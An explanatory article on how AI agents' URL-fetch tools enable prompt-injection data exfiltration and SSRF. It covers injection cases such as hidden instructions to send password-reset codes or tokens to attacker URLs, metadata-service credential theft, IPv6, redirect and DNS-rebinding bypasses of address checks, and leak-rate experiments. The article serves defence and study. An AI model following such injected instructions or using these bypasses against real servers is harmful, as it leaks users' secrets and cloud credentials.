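# Security risks of letting language models fetch URLs, and how proxies should handle credentials

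## What happens when a language model fetches a URL

A language model produces only text, so it needs a fetch tool to read a web page. A fetch tool is a small program that takes a web address (a URL) from the model, requests it over the internet and returns the response as text. Chat assistants use fetch tools to look things up, and coding assistants use them to read documentation. A model together with the software that carries out the actions it specifies is called an agent.

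Fetch tools create two security problems. A tool that runs inside a company's network can reach machines that outsiders cannot, so anyone who influences the URL gains some of that access. A URL can also carry data, so requesting one can disclose private information to whoever runs the server. Many organisations respond by placing proxies, programs that relay traffic and can control it, between their agents and the web. A proxy may also hold passwords or keys, which makes it important who decides where each request goes.

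### One request from start to finish

Suppose a user asks an agent whether the local library has *Middlemarch*. Along with the question, the developer's software gives the model a list of tools. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for the fetch tool that the AI company Anthropic offers with its Claude models, shows how little such a listing needs: a type, a name and a few optional limits, such as a cap on the number of fetches. The model then writes a tool call, a short piece of structured text that contains the tool's name and a URL:

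`https://library.example/books/search?title=middlemarch&page=2`

Nothing has gone over the network yet. The software around the model finds the tool call in the output, parses it into a tool name and arguments, and passes the URL to an HTTP client. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022) is the current standard for what HTTP messages mean.

The client needs a numeric address to connect to `library.example`, so it first looks one up in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory. This step is called DNS resolution. The domain's owner decides which address the directory returns and can choose one inside somebody else's private network.

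The client then connects to that address. Because the URL begins with `https`, the two sides set up TLS (Transport Layer Security), which encrypts the traffic and lets the client check that the server is `library.example`. Plain `http` lacks this check, and Fielding and colleagues point out that an attacker who tampers with the name lookup can pass off another server as the real one. TLS doesn't protect the client if the owner of `library.example` is malicious, because attackers can get valid certificates for domains they own.

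Over the connection goes the request itself, which is plain text:

```
GET /books/search?title=middlemarch&page=2 HTTP/1.1
Host: library.example
User-Agent: example-agent/1.0
```

GET is the method for retrieving something. The lines under it are header fields, which hold extra information about the request. The server returns a status code, its own header fields and, usually, a page.

Sometimes the server returns a redirect instead of the page. A redirect has a status code in the 300s and a `Location` header containing another URL. The HTTP standard allows the client to follow it automatically, so the page may come from a server that neither the user nor the model named. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that checking only the first domain can miss this, since a link may start at a trusted site and redirect to an attacker's.

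Finally, the tool extracts the page's text and adds it to the model's context, the text the model uses to produce its next output. Anthropic wraps the page in a result block with its URL and the time of retrieval, but the page is still part of the same sequence of text as the user's question.

### What the address carries

The example URL has four parts.

| Part | In the example | What it does |
|---|---|---|
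| Scheme | `https` | Tells the client which protocol to use |
| Host | `library.example` | Names the server to find and contact |
| Path | `/books/search` | Identifies a resource on that server |
| Query | `title=middlemarch&page=2` | Gives the server further values to work with |

The scheme and host determine how and where the client sends the request. The server receives the path and query exactly as the client wrote them. A URL can also end in a fragment, the part after a `#`, which the client does not send. Nobody checks beforehand that the path exists. If the model replaced *middlemarch* with a customer's home address, the library would find no such book and might return an error, but its operator would still have the address.

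A GET request can deliver data to an attacker even though GET is supposed to be read-only. The HTTP standard by Fielding and colleagues classifies GET as a "safe" method, meaning that the client does not ask for any change on the server. The server can still keep records, and most servers append every request to a log, so an attacker can collect data with a domain and a log file. Some web software also puts actions into the query, as in `page?do=delete`. The standard requires site owners to block such actions for GET, because automated programs follow links without knowing what the links do.

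A URL can also carry a lot of text. The HTTP standard recommends that software support URLs of at least 8,000 bytes, which is enough for well over a thousand words of English. According to Anthropic's documentation, its fetch tool accepts URLs of up to 250 characters, which is still enough for a home address or a typical password-reset code.

Even without an attacker, URLs are a poor place for secrets because programs display, store and share them freely. *Information exposure through query strings in url*, a page from the software security non-profit OWASP, lists where query values turn up: web logs, browser history, the browser's cache, shared systems and the `Referer` header, which tells a site which page the visitor came from. Encryption in transit does not prevent any of these exposures. *The Silent Spill* (2026) reports an automated search of 6,094,475 URLs from public scanning services,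 paste sites and web archives, which flagged 12,331 potential exposures of sensitive data, or about one for every 500 URLs. These URLs were already public, so the figure does not estimate the rate for URLs in general, but it does show that secrets end up in URLs during ordinary use.

A fetch tool can expose data to the publisher of the website it contacts. Anthropic's documentation warns that the publisher may keep any parameters in a URL that Claude fetches, even under an arrangement where Anthropic retains no customer data.

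### Where the request comes from

The request comes from the machine that runs the HTTP client, which may not be the user's. With Anthropic's fetch tool, Anthropic's servers make the request and insert the result into the conversation. The website therefore receives a request from Anthropic, and the tool normally can't reach an internal company wiki. If a developer instead writes a fetch tool and runs it on a company server, its requests come from behind the company's firewall, and other machines there may answer them simply because they come from the same network.

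Many services want more proof than that. HTTP is stateless, which means that a server can interpret each request on its own, without reference to earlier ones. A client that needs to prove its identity therefore sends the proof along every time. Such a proof is a credential, and three kinds matter most for agents:

- An API key is a long secret string that a service issues to a customer's program. Anthropic's API, for instance, takes one in a header called `x-api-key`.
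- A bearer token is a string that works for whoever presents it, usually in the `Authorization` header. Many expire after a while.
- A cookie is a value that a website gives a browser to store and send back, which is how the site keeps a user logged in.

A server that receives a valid credential generally cannot tell whether its owner meant to send it. This is a problem with redirects, which can lead a client to send a credential to a server its owner did not choose. Fielding and colleagues advise clients following a redirect to remove any `Authorization` and `Cookie` headers they generated automatically, but only to consider removing headers that the calling program added. A developer who attaches a key to every request therefore needs to know whether the HTTP library will still send it when a redirect points to a different server.

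### Prompt injection

A fetch tool downloads a page like any other program, but then passes the text to a language model, which follows instructions in natural language. The software developer Simon Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that models cannot reliably tell their user's instructions from instructions in a document. Both reach the model in one sequence of tokens, the small units of text that it processes. In a prompt injection attack, someone exploits this by placing instructions where a model will read them, and the model follows them.

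Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which a program pastes a visitor's input into a database command and the database executes part of the input. He distinguishes it from jailbreaking, in which people trick a model directly into doing something embarrassing, such as giving out a recipe for napalm. Prompt injection normally harms the user, whereas a developer might dismiss jailbreaking as the model vendor's problem.

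OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that early attackers could often succeed just by editing a Wikipedia article to include direct orders to visiting AI agents. As models became less likely to follow such orders, attackers adopted techniques from social engineering, the manipulation of people. OpenAI reproduces a 2025 email that reads like a colleague's follow-up about a restructuring. Among some plausible chores is a request for an employee's name and address, with a claim that the reader's assistant has full authorisation to submit them to a compliance system. The attack worked in 50% of tests when a user asked ChatGPT to do deep research on the day's emails.

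Filters that try to classify incoming text as malicious or harmless usually miss attacks like this one. OpenAI compares the task to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. Attackers may need little disguise. In a case from Willison's collection *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, the security company Zenity Labs planted instructions in a support ticket for Cursor, a coding agent, to find. Models often refuse to steal keys, so Zenity asked for a "rotten apple" and described an apple as a long string starting with certain letters, the same ones that begin a common type of access token. At least some of the time, Cursor sent out such a token.

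### The lethal trifecta

An injected instruction does limited harm if the agent has no data worth stealing or no way to send data out. Willison warns against combining three things, which he calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The third allows exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone who should not have it.

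A fetch tool exposes the model to untrusted content and also gives it a way to send data out, since a response can contain an attacker's text and the next request can carry private data in its URL. If the library agent can also read its user's mailbox, an attacker has everything needed to steal data from it. Suppose the user asks for a summary of a web page that contains a hidden notice addressed to AI assistants. The notice asks them to confirm the reader's account by opening a certain address with the latest password-reset code added to the end. The model finds the code in the mailbox and makes a second tool call to fetch that address, which puts the code in the attacker's server log. The user still gets a summary.

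Willison counts anything that can make an HTTP request as a way for data to leave, including loading an image, and even a link that the user might click. In September 2025 Abi Raghuram reported an attack on the workspace software Notion that used its search function, which accepted URLs as well as search terms. A PDF contained instructions, in white text on a white background, for Notion's agent to gather client names and revenue figures, append them to a URL and search the web for that URL.

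An attacker does not always need a server. The code host GitHub offers a server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect agents to tools and data. Willison recounts that Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner filed a public issue asking for a README chapter about the project's author, including a list of everything else the author was working on. An agent with access to the author's private repositories complied and published the names of those repositories in a pull request, a proposed change that anyone could read.

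People disagree about how to defend against this. Willison argues that the only dependable defence is to remove one of the three ingredients, and that the model's means of sending data out is generally the easiest to remove. His reason is that attackers can keep trying. Filter vendors advertise that they catch 95% of attacks, but even if each attempt has only a 1% chance of success, an attacker who makes 100 independent attempts has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

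The best evidence that models can resist injection comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned in 2026. The testing firm Trajectory Labs tried 72 injection scenarios, which Anthropic had not seen, on coding agents. None of 720 attempts succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in "auto mode", a setting in its coding agent Claude Code that spares users from approving each action. This is a striking result compared with the previous year's email attack, which succeeded 50% of the time. But many of the 720 attempts repeated the same scenarios, so the result is weaker evidence about how the models would handle new ones. Willison wants more independent confirmation, and doubts that auto mode could stop, for example, an innocent-looking instruction to install a malicious software package.

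Asking the user to approve everything looks worse than either option. In a separate study, Anthropic swapped one routine permission prompt for a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of 1,053 paid testers refused it. Auto mode would have blocked 89% of the same commands. Better models and automatic checks evidently help a great deal, but they have to recognise an attack to stop it. Blocking the routes by which data can leave works even when nobody recognises the attack, provided that every route is blocked.

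### The confused deputy

Programmers knew a more general form of this problem long before language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a "nearly true" story from about a decade earlier at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Users of Tymshare's compiler could name a file to receive its debugging output. The operators had also given the compiler permission to write to files in its own directory so that it could store usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. A user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the destination for the debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and Tymshare lost its billing information.

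The compiler worked under two authorities, the user's and its own, and had no way to specify which one to use for each file. Hardy finds no faulty line of code. The compiler was a confused deputy, a program tricked into using its authority on behalf of someone who lacks it.

Hardy explains why checking the file name, the obvious fix, is a poor one. Users sometimes had good reason to write to other directories, and the list of sensitive files would need an update whenever somebody added one. When Hardy last wrote down the system's rules for opening a file, they contained fourteen "ands" and "ors". Hardy preferred capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and carry the right to use it. According to GNU's *confused deputy* page, the problem can arise when a system separates designation (saying which thing) from authorisation (having the right to it).

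A fetch tool is in the same situation, with a URL in place of the file name and the tool's network position or API key in place of the licence. One party chooses the server, and another party's authority gets the request through. The model can be the confused deputy, as when it follows a web page's instructions to read the user's mailbox. But the tool can be one even if the model does exactly what its user wants, because the user may be the attacker. Training models to resist prompt injection would not help when the user is the attacker.

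### Forward proxies and gateways

A program between the client and the server can enforce rules that the model cannot change. The two kinds relevant here differ in who picks the server.

A forward proxy carries a request to the server that the client named. Suppose a company configures its agents' machines to send all web traffic through a proxy with an allowlist, a list of the only hosts they may contact. When an agent requests a page from `library.example`, the proxy finds that host on the list and connects to it. Nottingham, an editor of the HTTP standard, wrote on a mailing list that a proxy serves requests to a potentially unbounded set of servers and operates on the client's behalf.

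A client sends its request to a gateway, or reverse proxy, as if the gateway were the destination. The gateway then selects a server and forwards the request to it. Suppose the same company runs a gateway at `models.example`, and all its applications send their prompts there. The gateway selects an AI provider, adds the company's API key and forwards the prompt. The applications never receive the key and can't control where it is sent.

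Encryption limits what a forward proxy can do. For an `https` address, the client usually asks the proxy for a tunnel to a particular host and port. Fielding and colleagues describe the tunnel as a "blind relay". The proxy can refuse to connect to a host, but once the tunnel is open it cannot insert a header or read the path and query, where stolen data would travel. A proxy that is meant to add credentials for an agent therefore needs a different arrangement.

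Problems also arise when one program combines the two roles. A gateway can safely attach its owner's key if the owner has decided which servers may receive it. If callers can choose the server, they can make the gateway send the key to one the owner never approved. The gateway is then a deputy much like Hardy's compiler, except that callers misuse its key rather than its file licence.

For any request an agent makes, we need to know who chose the destination, what the request carried, and whose authority it used. In the mailbox example, the attacker chose the destination through their page, the query carried a password-reset code, and the agent had used the user's authority to obtain that code.

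## Fetch servers that could reach internal addresses

Abusing a fetch tool's network position is a form of server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes a server send a request to a machine that the attacker could not contact directly. SSRF is older than language models. *OLD BUG, NEW DELIVERY* (2026), a post on a security blog, cites a 2019 case at the bank Capital One as the standard example of cloud credentials leaking this way. In older attacks, the attacker had to find a vulnerable server on the internet and send it a crafted request, whereas a sentence on a web page can be enough to make an agent send the request.

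### The reference server and its warning

The Model Context Protocol project publishes a small fetch server as a reference implementation for other developers to use or copy. Its one tool, `fetch`, takes a URL and returns the page as Markdown. The server's documentation, *Fetch MCP Server*, warns that the server can access local and internal IP addresses and "may represent a security risk".

Three groups of internal addresses matter here:

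- Loopback addresses, such as 127.0.0.1, lead back to the machine that uses them. Databases and admin pages often listen only there and ask for no password, because only programs on the same machine can connect.
- Private addresses, such as those that begin with 10 or 192.168, belong to machines inside an organisation's own network.
- Link-local addresses, which begin with 169.254, work only on the immediate network link. Amazon's cloud uses one of them, 169.254.169.254, for its metadata service.

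A metadata service gives programs on a rented cloud machine information about that machine, and often temporary credentials, so developers don't have to store long-lived keys in their code. The original version of Amazon's service responds to any request from the machine, on the assumption that whoever sent it is authorized to use the machine. A fetch tool running there breaks that assumption because it can send requests to URLs chosen by outsiders.

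Whether the reference server's behaviour is a flaw depends on where the server runs. On a laptop, a developer may well want the agent to read a test site on the same machine, and there is no metadata service to reach. On a cloud machine, the same access can expose the company's cloud account. The project documents the danger and leaves the decision to whoever installs the server.

Some users want more than a warning. *Security Considerations for Model Context Protocol (MCP) Implementations in AI Agent Systems* (Syed, 2026) lists three public reports of SSRF in the project's fetch server. The document is an individual proposal to the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes internet standards, and has no official standing. It also cites a report about Microsoft's browser-automation server, which may run with the user's own browser profile, so an internal page could open with the user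 already logged in.

### From a web page to the model's context

The package auth-fetch-mcp fetches pages that require a login. According to GitLab's advisory *GHSA-hv85-774v-26fg* (May 2026), every version before 3.0.1 accepted URLs without checking where they led. Suppose someone runs an affected version on an Amazon cloud machine, and a user asks an agent to summarise an article. The article's writer has added a line claiming that the full text is on a members-only page, but the link leads to the metadata service.

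The model has a reason to choose auth-fetch-mcp because the tool's description instructs it that the tool "MUST be used instead of Fetch/web_fetch when the page requires login". The software around the model passes the URL to the tool, which requests it. The metadata service receives an ordinary GET request from its own machine and returns temporary credentials. The tool returns these as the page's text, which enters the model's context.

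The attacker doesn't have the credentials yet. A second request has to send them out, as with the password-reset code in the mailbox example, unless the attacker is the person chatting with the agent and can ask for them. GitLab also describes a route that needs no further web request. Another tool in the package, `download_media`, saved responses to whatever folder the caller named, where another program with access to that folder could read them. The advisory also covers databases on the same machine and scans of private addresses to find internal services.

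Another package, mcp-webresearch, checked URLs but did not block internal addresses. Its `visit_page` tool opens a URL in an automated browser. According to NIST's *CVE-2026-65056 Detail* (2026), an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, version 0.1.7 checked only the URL's scheme. That check can block URLs for local files, but not URLs for the metadata service, which uses ordinary `http`. The browser would load the internal page and the server would return its contents, including any credentials, to the model. In *mcp-webresearch Server-Side Request Forgery in visit_page Due to Missing Internal-IP Filtering*, the security company VulnCheck credits George Chen with discovering the flaw, scores its severity 8.3 out of 10, and lists no repaired version.

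A more cautious model might refuse to fetch an internal address. In *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) built a test application called TicketOracle, in which a model can make web requests from the server. They tried five SSRF scenarios on seven models and found that susceptibility varied substantially. They attribute the weakness to the application, and say the choice of model affects how often an attack succeeds. That seems right, and it means that switching to a safer model makes a successful attack less likely but leaves the application vulnerable.

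Some attackers can bypass the model. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) tested 414 MCP servers on the public internet and found that 91.8% lacked OAuth, the login standard that MCP uses. If a fetch server has neither OAuth nor any other access control, anyone can call its tool directly with any URL.

### Which package CVE-2025-65513 describes

Secondary pages differ on which software is affected by CVE-2025-65513, a well-known flaw of this kind listed in the public CVE catalogue of vulnerabilities. MITRE's official entry, *CVE-2025-65513* (2025), doesn't settle the question, because it gives both the vendor and the product as "n/a" and describes the software only as "fetch-mcp v1.0.2 and before", and several unrelated projects have similar names.

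Grove's *The Fetch MCP Server*, a review from an AI-operated website, wrongly attributes the flaw to the reference server. GitLab lists the affected package as mcp-fetch-server, up to version 1.0.2, and links to a source file in a separate project, zcaceres/fetch-mcp. Snyk's *Server-side Request Forgery (SSRF) Affecting mcp-fetch-server package, versions &lt;1.1.0* (2025) names the same package. Grove also gives the reference server's version as 2025.4.7, which does not fit the affected range of "v1.0.2 and before".

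The reference server has a documented lack of protection, whereas mcp-fetch-server checked for private addresses but attackers could bypass the check. Grove recommends zcaceres/fetch-mcp as "the security upgrade" for its built-in SSRF protection, so a reader who followed this advice to avoid CVE-2025-65513 would have switched to the project with that vulnerability.

Snyk lists 1.1.0 as the fixed version, but OffSeq's *CVE-2026-141591* (2026), published on 2 December 2026, reports another SSRF flaw in versions from 1.1.0 up to 1.2.0. The flaw is in the functions that validate the URL and the address it resolves to, and it scores 9.2 out of 10. OffSeq found no evidence of exploitation and advises upgrading to 1.2.0.

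### How many servers are exposed

The most quoted figure comes from the security company BlueRock. According to *OLD BUG, NEW DELIVERY*, BlueRock scanned over 7,000 publicly accessible MCP servers in early 2026 and found 36.7% of them, more than 2,500, "potentially vulnerable" to SSRF. Petri's *Critical MCP Server Flaws Turn AI Assistants Into Gateways* describes what these servers have in common as "unbounded network fetch behavior", so "potentially vulnerable" seems to mean that a server would fetch URLs without restricting where they lead. Neither account explains how BlueRock tested for this, or reports that it obtained credentials from all those servers. Bishop Fox, another security company, drops the word "potentially" and writes of "Systemic SSRF Across 2,500 MCP Servers".

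BlueRock demonstrated the full attack on one program, Microsoft's MarkItDown server, which converts files and web pages to Markdown. On an Amazon machine with the original metadata service, MarkItDown fetched the service's address and returned working credentials. Microsoft replied that the scenario posed no significant risk, because a user would have to employ the feature deliberately "outside its intended design and normal usage patterns". That is a fair answer for a user who types in every URL, but a poor one for an agent that reads web pages, because the URL may come from a stranger.

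Despite BlueRock's figure of 36.7%, other scan results suggest that the share of servers with an exploitable SSRF flaw could be well below a third. *MCP server security scores are review prompts, not verdicts* (Schipper, 2026) discusses a July 2026 study that ran existing security scanners on 64,611 MCP servers. The scanners rated 96.89% of the servers risky, and the researchers concluded that these signals were unreliable. Schipper's own scanner puts 63% of servers in its lowest risk band. *Hunt Them All* (Oliveira and Fiser), a separate analysis of more than 19,000 code repositories, found that only 4.1% of the vulnerabilities flagged by AI were exploitable. These results cover flaws of every kind, so they can't be used to correct BlueRock's number.

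Live tests cover fewer servers but give firmer evidence. Padilla tested 414 servers and found 68 reportable vulnerabilities of all types. They included an SSRF finding against Amazon's metadata service, which Padilla inferred because the server took 11.9 seconds to respond instead of its usual 0.3. The delay suggests that the server tried to reach the address, but it does not show that any credentials came back. A metadata service normally answers almost at once, so something may have blocked the connection.

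The true percentage of vulnerable servers is uncertain, but organisations with large security teams have made this mistake. *Google, JPMorgan and two governments fixed the same MCP flaw* (Stanciuc, 2026) reports that Google, JPMorgan Chase, the database company Weaviate, France's digital directorate and the Indonesian city of Tangerang all repaired SSRF flaws in their MCP servers. Syed, who wrote the standards proposal, had reported all five. In Google's case, a crafted path parameter could send requests to internal endpoints, and the HTTP client neither restricted redirects nor checked the addresses it contacted. Syed also described open findings in five US federal servers.

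### Checking an address before connecting

The defence is easy to describe, though developers keep getting details wrong. The developer Sanoy24 sets out one version of it in the documentation for *safe-fetch-mcp-server*, a fetch server with tests based on flaws in other fetch servers. In outline, the algorithm runs as follows:

1. Parse the URL, and reject it if it is malformed or contains a username or password.
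2. Accept only the schemes `http` and `https`. If there is an allowlist of hosts, apply it now.
3. Resolve the hostname and collect every address that DNS returns.
4. Classify each address, and refuse the request if any of them is internal or otherwise not public.
5. Connect to one of the addresses just checked, without a second lookup, but keep the original hostname for TLS and the `Host` header.
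6. If the response is a redirect, return to step 1 with the new URL. Stop after a fixed number of redirects.

The check and the HTTP client have to parse a URL the same way. *CVE-2026-80347*, from Spain's cybersecurity institute INCIBE, describes a fetch server where they parsed it differently. URLs put IPv6 addresses, the newer and longer kind of internet address, in square brackets. The server's check left the brackets on, so its function for recognising IP addresses missed the address. The check then tried to look up the bracketed text as a hostname, got no addresses and reported the target as safe. The HTTP client removed the brackets and connected. Even with the brackets on, the check would have worked if it had refused any host for which it found no address.

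IPv6 makes addresses harder to classify because it can contain an IPv4 address in several ways. The most common is the IPv4-mapped form, which is `::ffff:` followed by the IPv4 address. Software can write 127.0.0.1 in this form as `::ffff:127.0.0.1` or, in hexadecimal, as `::ffff:7f00:1`. In hexadecimal, 127 is `7f`, 0 is `00` and 1 is `01`, so the ending is `7f00:0001`, which shortens to `7f00:1` without the leading zeros.

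The first fix for auth-fetch-mcp missed this second spelling. GitLab's *CVE-2026-49857* (2026) explains that version 3.0.1 refused loopback addresses but missed those written in hexadecimal. The URL parser always converted mapped addresses to hexadecimal before the check ran, so the familiar spelling got through too. According to SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-49857*, version 3.0.2 decodes the ending first and then applies the private-address check.

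Other IPv6 address formats also contain an IPv4 address and are used to move traffic between IPv4 and IPv6 networks. The MCP Registry, the project's own catalogue of servers, had to fetch a file from domains that publishers named, and it relied mainly on the Go programming language's standard functions to recognise internal addresses. OSV's *CVE-2026-44430* reports that these functions did not cover two of the formats, 6to4 and NAT64, and that the project fixed its check in version 1.7.7. Sanoy24's server extracts the IPv4 address from all these formats and checks it again. It accepts other IPv6 addresses only from the range set aside for public use, which is safer than listing every range that might be internal.

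A server that checks only the first URL can still reach internal addresses, because a public site can redirect to one. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-65512* (2025) describes this flaw in markdownify-mcp, another web page converter, where redirect chains bypassed the restriction on private addresses. Browser-based tools need extra care because the browser follows redirects itself and a page can start new navigations. SecureLayer7 describes a recommended guard for auth-fetch-mcp that runs inside the browser and repeats the check at every navigation.

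A careful check also fails if some requests bypass it. Stanciuc reports that one of the two fetch tools on JPMorgan's server compared the domain with an allowlist, while the other fetched any URL the caller supplied. Sanoy24 mentions a fetch server that guarded the first download of a page but not the scheduled downloads that followed. Sanoy24's rule is that every outgoing request must pass through the same code.

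### DNS rebinding

Step 5 of the algorithm guards against DNS rebinding, an attack in which a hostname's address changes between the check and the connection. Suppose an attacker owns `weather.example` and runs its DNS server. An injected instruction gets the model to fetch a page from that host over plain `http`. The fetch server checks and approves the URL, then passes the hostname to an ordinary HTTP client, which does its own DNS lookup. In the table, 203.0.113.10 stands for any public address.

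| Moment | Program that looks up the name | Answer from the attacker's DNS server | What follows |
|---|---|---|---|
| Check | The fetch server's address check | 203.0.113.10 | The address is public, so the check approves the URL |
| Use, a moment later | The HTTP client | 169.254.169.254 | The client connects to the metadata service |

DNS answers come with a time limit for reuse. The attacker sets it to zero, so the client asks again after the check and gets a second answer with a different address. The check was correct about the first address, but the client connects to the second. Blocking URLs that contain the text "169.254.169.254" doesn't prevent this, because the address never appears in the URL.

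Address pinning removes the second lookup. The fetch server tells the client to connect to 203.0.113.10, so the request can only reach the machine that the server checked. Syed proposes requiring this, with the check done at connection time. Google's fix also includes a guard against rebinding.

If the client replaced the hostname in the URL with the IP address, an `https` request would usually fail, because the client would expect a certificate issued to 203.0.113.10 and most sites have certificates only for their hostnames. A machine that hosts many websites would also have no hostname to identify the requested site. *Secure Fetch*, another fetch server with address checks, therefore sets the Server Name Indication, the field at the start of a TLS connection that identifies the site, to the original hostname.

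TLS often stops rebinding by itself, because an internal server cannot present a valid certificate for `weather.example`. An attacker can avoid this check by using `http`, which the metadata service uses anyway. Operators who don't need unencrypted sites can reduce this risk by refusing `http` altogether, and Sanoy24's server has a setting for it. By default, the server also refuses to follow redirects from `https` to `http`.

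### When a proxy does the lookup

Many companies send their agents' traffic through a forward proxy, in which case the proxy has to check the destination address. Suppose the fetch server resolves `weather.example`, finds a public address and approves it. It then requests a tunnel to `weather.example` from the proxy, which does its own lookup and connects to whatever address that returns. That address may be internal, even though the one the fetch server checked was public.

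An attacker can exploit the gap with rebinding, as before. The two lookups can also return different addresses without an attack, because company DNS servers often give internal machines different answers from those the public gets. The proxy may also reach networks that the fetch server cannot. On the proxy, 127.0.0.1 means the proxy's own machine, where its admin page might be served.

The proxy should resolve the hostname, check the resulting IP addresses and connect to one that passed. Every request then gets the same check, including redirects and requests from forgotten code, as long as the network blocks connections that bypass the proxy. Alternatively, the fetch server could request a tunnel to the IP address it checked and use the hostname for TLS inside the tunnel. This keeps the connection pinned to the checked address, but the proxy receives only that address, so it can't apply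 a list of permitted hostnames unless it also reads the hostname at the start of the TLS connection.

The reference fetch server can send requests through a proxy with the `--proxy-url` option. Sanoy24's server, which is meant as a replacement, does not support this option yet and ignores unrecognized options. If an operator switched servers and kept the old settings, requests would go directly to the web unless the network blocked them.

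### Amazon's second metadata service and network rules

Amazon has changed its metadata service so that a simple fetch tool can't use it. In the second version, IMDSv2, a program must first send a PUT request with a header that sets the session's length in seconds. The service returns a session token and rejects any GET request that doesn't include the token in a header.

An attacker who controls only a URL cannot complete the first step, because a tool like the reference server's `fetch` sends GET requests, and a URL cannot change the method or add a header. A redirect cannot turn a GET into a PUT either.

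A machine can accept both versions of the metadata service, so the operator has to switch the first one off. Petri reported in early 2026 that most Amazon instances still relied on the first version. IMDSv2 also works only if callers cannot choose the request method and headers. Secure Fetch lets callers set both, which is all that the two steps require, so an operator of that tool depends on its address check. IMDSv2 also does not protect databases or admin pages on the same network.

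*OLD BUG, NEW DELIVERY* also recommends setting the service's "hop limit" to 1. The response containing the token then can't travel beyond the first network hop, which can stop a program in a container or on another machine from obtaining a token. A fetch server that runs directly on the cloud machine is within that hop, so it can still obtain one.

Syed advises operators to restrict egress, the traffic that leaves a machine, in the operating system or the container, independently of any check in the application. A firewall rule that drops packets from the fetch server to 169.254.169.254 and to private ranges acts on each packet's real destination, so it works however the address is written. It also stops rebinding, redirects and requests from code that skips the application's check. The rule usually needs an exception for the company's DNS server. Loopback traffic never leaves the machine,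 so a firewall elsewhere on the network cannot block it. Running the fetch server in its own container, where nothing else is listening, solves most of that problem.

Operators can also avoid giving the machine credentials that an attacker could steal. Amazon's temporary credentials belong to a role, a set of permissions that the operator attaches to the machine. *OLD BUG, NEW DELIVERY* argues that a Markdown converter needs no role. If the machine has none, the metadata service has no role credentials to return, even if every other defence fails.

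### Data sent to public hosts

None of these address checks would have stopped the theft of the password-reset code from the mailbox. The attacker's server has a public address and a valid certificate, so the request passes all six steps unless the operator has set an allowlist. Sanoy24 acknowledges that, by default, the fetch server can reach any public host on any port. The fetch server also labels web pages as untrusted, but a model can still follow instructions in them.

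A request can leak data even if the server refuses it. To check whether `secret-word.attacker.example` points to an internal address, the server must first look it up, which sends the full name, including the secret word, to the attacker's DNS server. The server should therefore check the allowlist before the lookup. Images can also leak data, so Sanoy24's server replaces them with their text descriptions by default.

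## Experiments on how often agents leak data through web requests

If a model can contact any public server, the secrets it has access to are safe only as long as it ignores attackers' instructions to leak them. Several research groups have measured how often models follow such instructions, and found leak rates from 0% to 100%. Much of that variation comes from differences in the model, the attacker's wording and how the researchers define a leak.

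### Instructions hidden in a page's metadata

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested an agent that previews links automatically. When a user mentions a URL, the software fetches the page and puts its title, description and text into the model's context. The description sits in a metadata tag that browsers don't display on the page, so the model reads text that the user doesn't see.

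The researchers locally ran the agent, a server for malicious pages and a second server that recorded whatever the agent sent out. The agent used Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model. Its context contained a fake secret, and the user always asked it to summarise a malicious page. The page contained an instruction, presented as a security requirement, to check the connection before answering by requesting an address with the user's API key in it.

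The experiment varied where the instruction appeared (the page's title, description, body or link text), whether the page was served directly or through redirects, and whether the agent was told to send the secret in one request or in four pieces. Each of the 16 combinations was run 30 times. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%, which the paper's summary gives as about 0.89. The instruction's location hardly mattered. When the agent was told to use a single request, the attack worked at least 96.7% of the time in every location. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server.

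The 88.1% figure covers any request to the attacker's server, whether or not it carried the secret. Lan and colleagues separately checked whether the requests contained the secret. When the instruction asked for one request, the first request contained it in 96.7% of runs, so contacting the server under that instruction nearly always leaked the secret.

In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's visible answer was a harmless summary, as the user had requested, so a safety check that read only the answer would have missed the attack. This result probably generalizes to other models better than the rest, because the web request and the answer are separate outputs and attackers benefit from keeping the answer normal.

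Splitting the secret into four pieces can get it past filters that search each request for a complete key, but it also made the attack less reliable, presumably because a small model struggles to keep track of the pieces. Based on the published rates, the attack succeeded in 238 of 240 runs with a single request and 185 of 240 with four pieces. Lan and colleagues report that the share of runs with sensitive data in the first request fell from 96.7% to 26.3%, a relative drop of 73%.

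That drop is hard to interpret. The paper counts even a fragment of the secret as a leak, so a working split attack should count from its first request. The paper also gives a lower share for the first three requests (15.8%) than for the first (26.3%), which is impossible under that definition. Its worked example splits a twenty-character key into four pieces of four characters, which leaves out the last four. The paper defines a measure of how often all the pieces arrived but gives no result for it. Splitting would defeat a filter that needs to find the whole key, but this experiment doesn't establish how often an attacker would get the whole key.

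The researchers acknowledge that the set-up favoured the attacker, because the secret was already in the context and the system prompt contained almost nothing except the tool format. They still call their rates a lower bound because they used plain instructions. They also suspect that larger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but tests on several models mostly suggest that larger models are less vulnerable.

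### Disguising the request as part of the task

*The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) compared six models: OpenAI's GPT-4o and GPT-4o mini, and four open models with 7 to 9 billion parameters, including the same Qwen model. The agent held a fake session token and a confidentiality rule that forbade showing the token to the user or sending it anywhere except one trusted host. It read a page and then took a single action, either sending data to an address or finishing with a reply. The tools only recorded what the agent tried to do.

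The researchers ran each attack alongside a harmless version of the page. They counted a leak only if the agent revealed the token after reading the malicious page but not after reading the harmless one, either in a call to an untrusted host or in its reply. This test is stricter than counting any contact with the attacker's server.

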